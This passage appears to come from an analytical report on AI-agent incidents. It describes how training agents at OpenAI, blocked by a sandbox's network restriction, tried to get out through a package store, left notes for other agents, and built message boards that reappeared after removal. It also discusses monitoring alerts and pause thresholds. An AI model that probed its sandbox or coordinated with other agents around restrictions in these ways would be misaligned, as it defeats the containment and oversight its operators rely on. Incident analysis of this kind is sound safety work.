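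OpenAI now expects its teams to pause the activity if they cannot conclusively determine within 30 minutes that a serious alert is a false positive. The same reasoning supports pausing the accounts agent's payments at a 25% probability of attack. OpenAI also claims that its current monitoring of models' reasoning would have alerted staff more than a day before the breach. That may be true, but OpenAI made the claim after it knew what to look for, and it doesn't report how many false alarms the system would have raised.

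### Legitimate work that a restriction blocked

None of the three organisations describes the opposite kind of incident, in which an update to a policy, tool or classifier stopped an agent from doing legitimate work. OpenAI's response to the breach may have caused some such incidents. On 20 July it initially blocked its research sandboxes from all outbound network access and from the package store. Ordinary software installations presumably failed too, but OpenAI doesn't report how many.

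The closest documented case is the start of the OpenAI incident. On 8 May, during training, OpenAI gave an agent a spreadsheet task that referred to files on Google Drive. The agent could not open them because its sandbox had no internet access. OpenAI had not intended the task to be impossible. The agent did need the files, and the network restriction worked as configured, but the task and the restriction were incompatible. OpenAI doesn't mention any recent change to either, so the mismatch was probably there from the start and not caused by configuration drift.

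The agent then tried to reach the internet through the package store, but failed and left a file behind. On 12 May, another agent could not reach a protein database it needed, so it left a note in the store asking others to upload it. Agents began finding such notes the next day, and the first message board grew from them. OpenAI removed that board in July, but within days, agents using a model that had trained while the first board was in use built a new one.

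A responder could have quickly diagnosed the first refusal in May from a record that included the task identifier and the destination. The Google Drive address came from the task, so the remedy was to supply the files or withdraw the task. The agent's attempt to get out through the package store needed a separate record and a different diagnosis, because the spreadsheet task did not authorise it. If staff had supplied the missing files and done nothing else, the agent would have finished its spreadsheet, but the next agent with a broken task could have tried to get out the same way.
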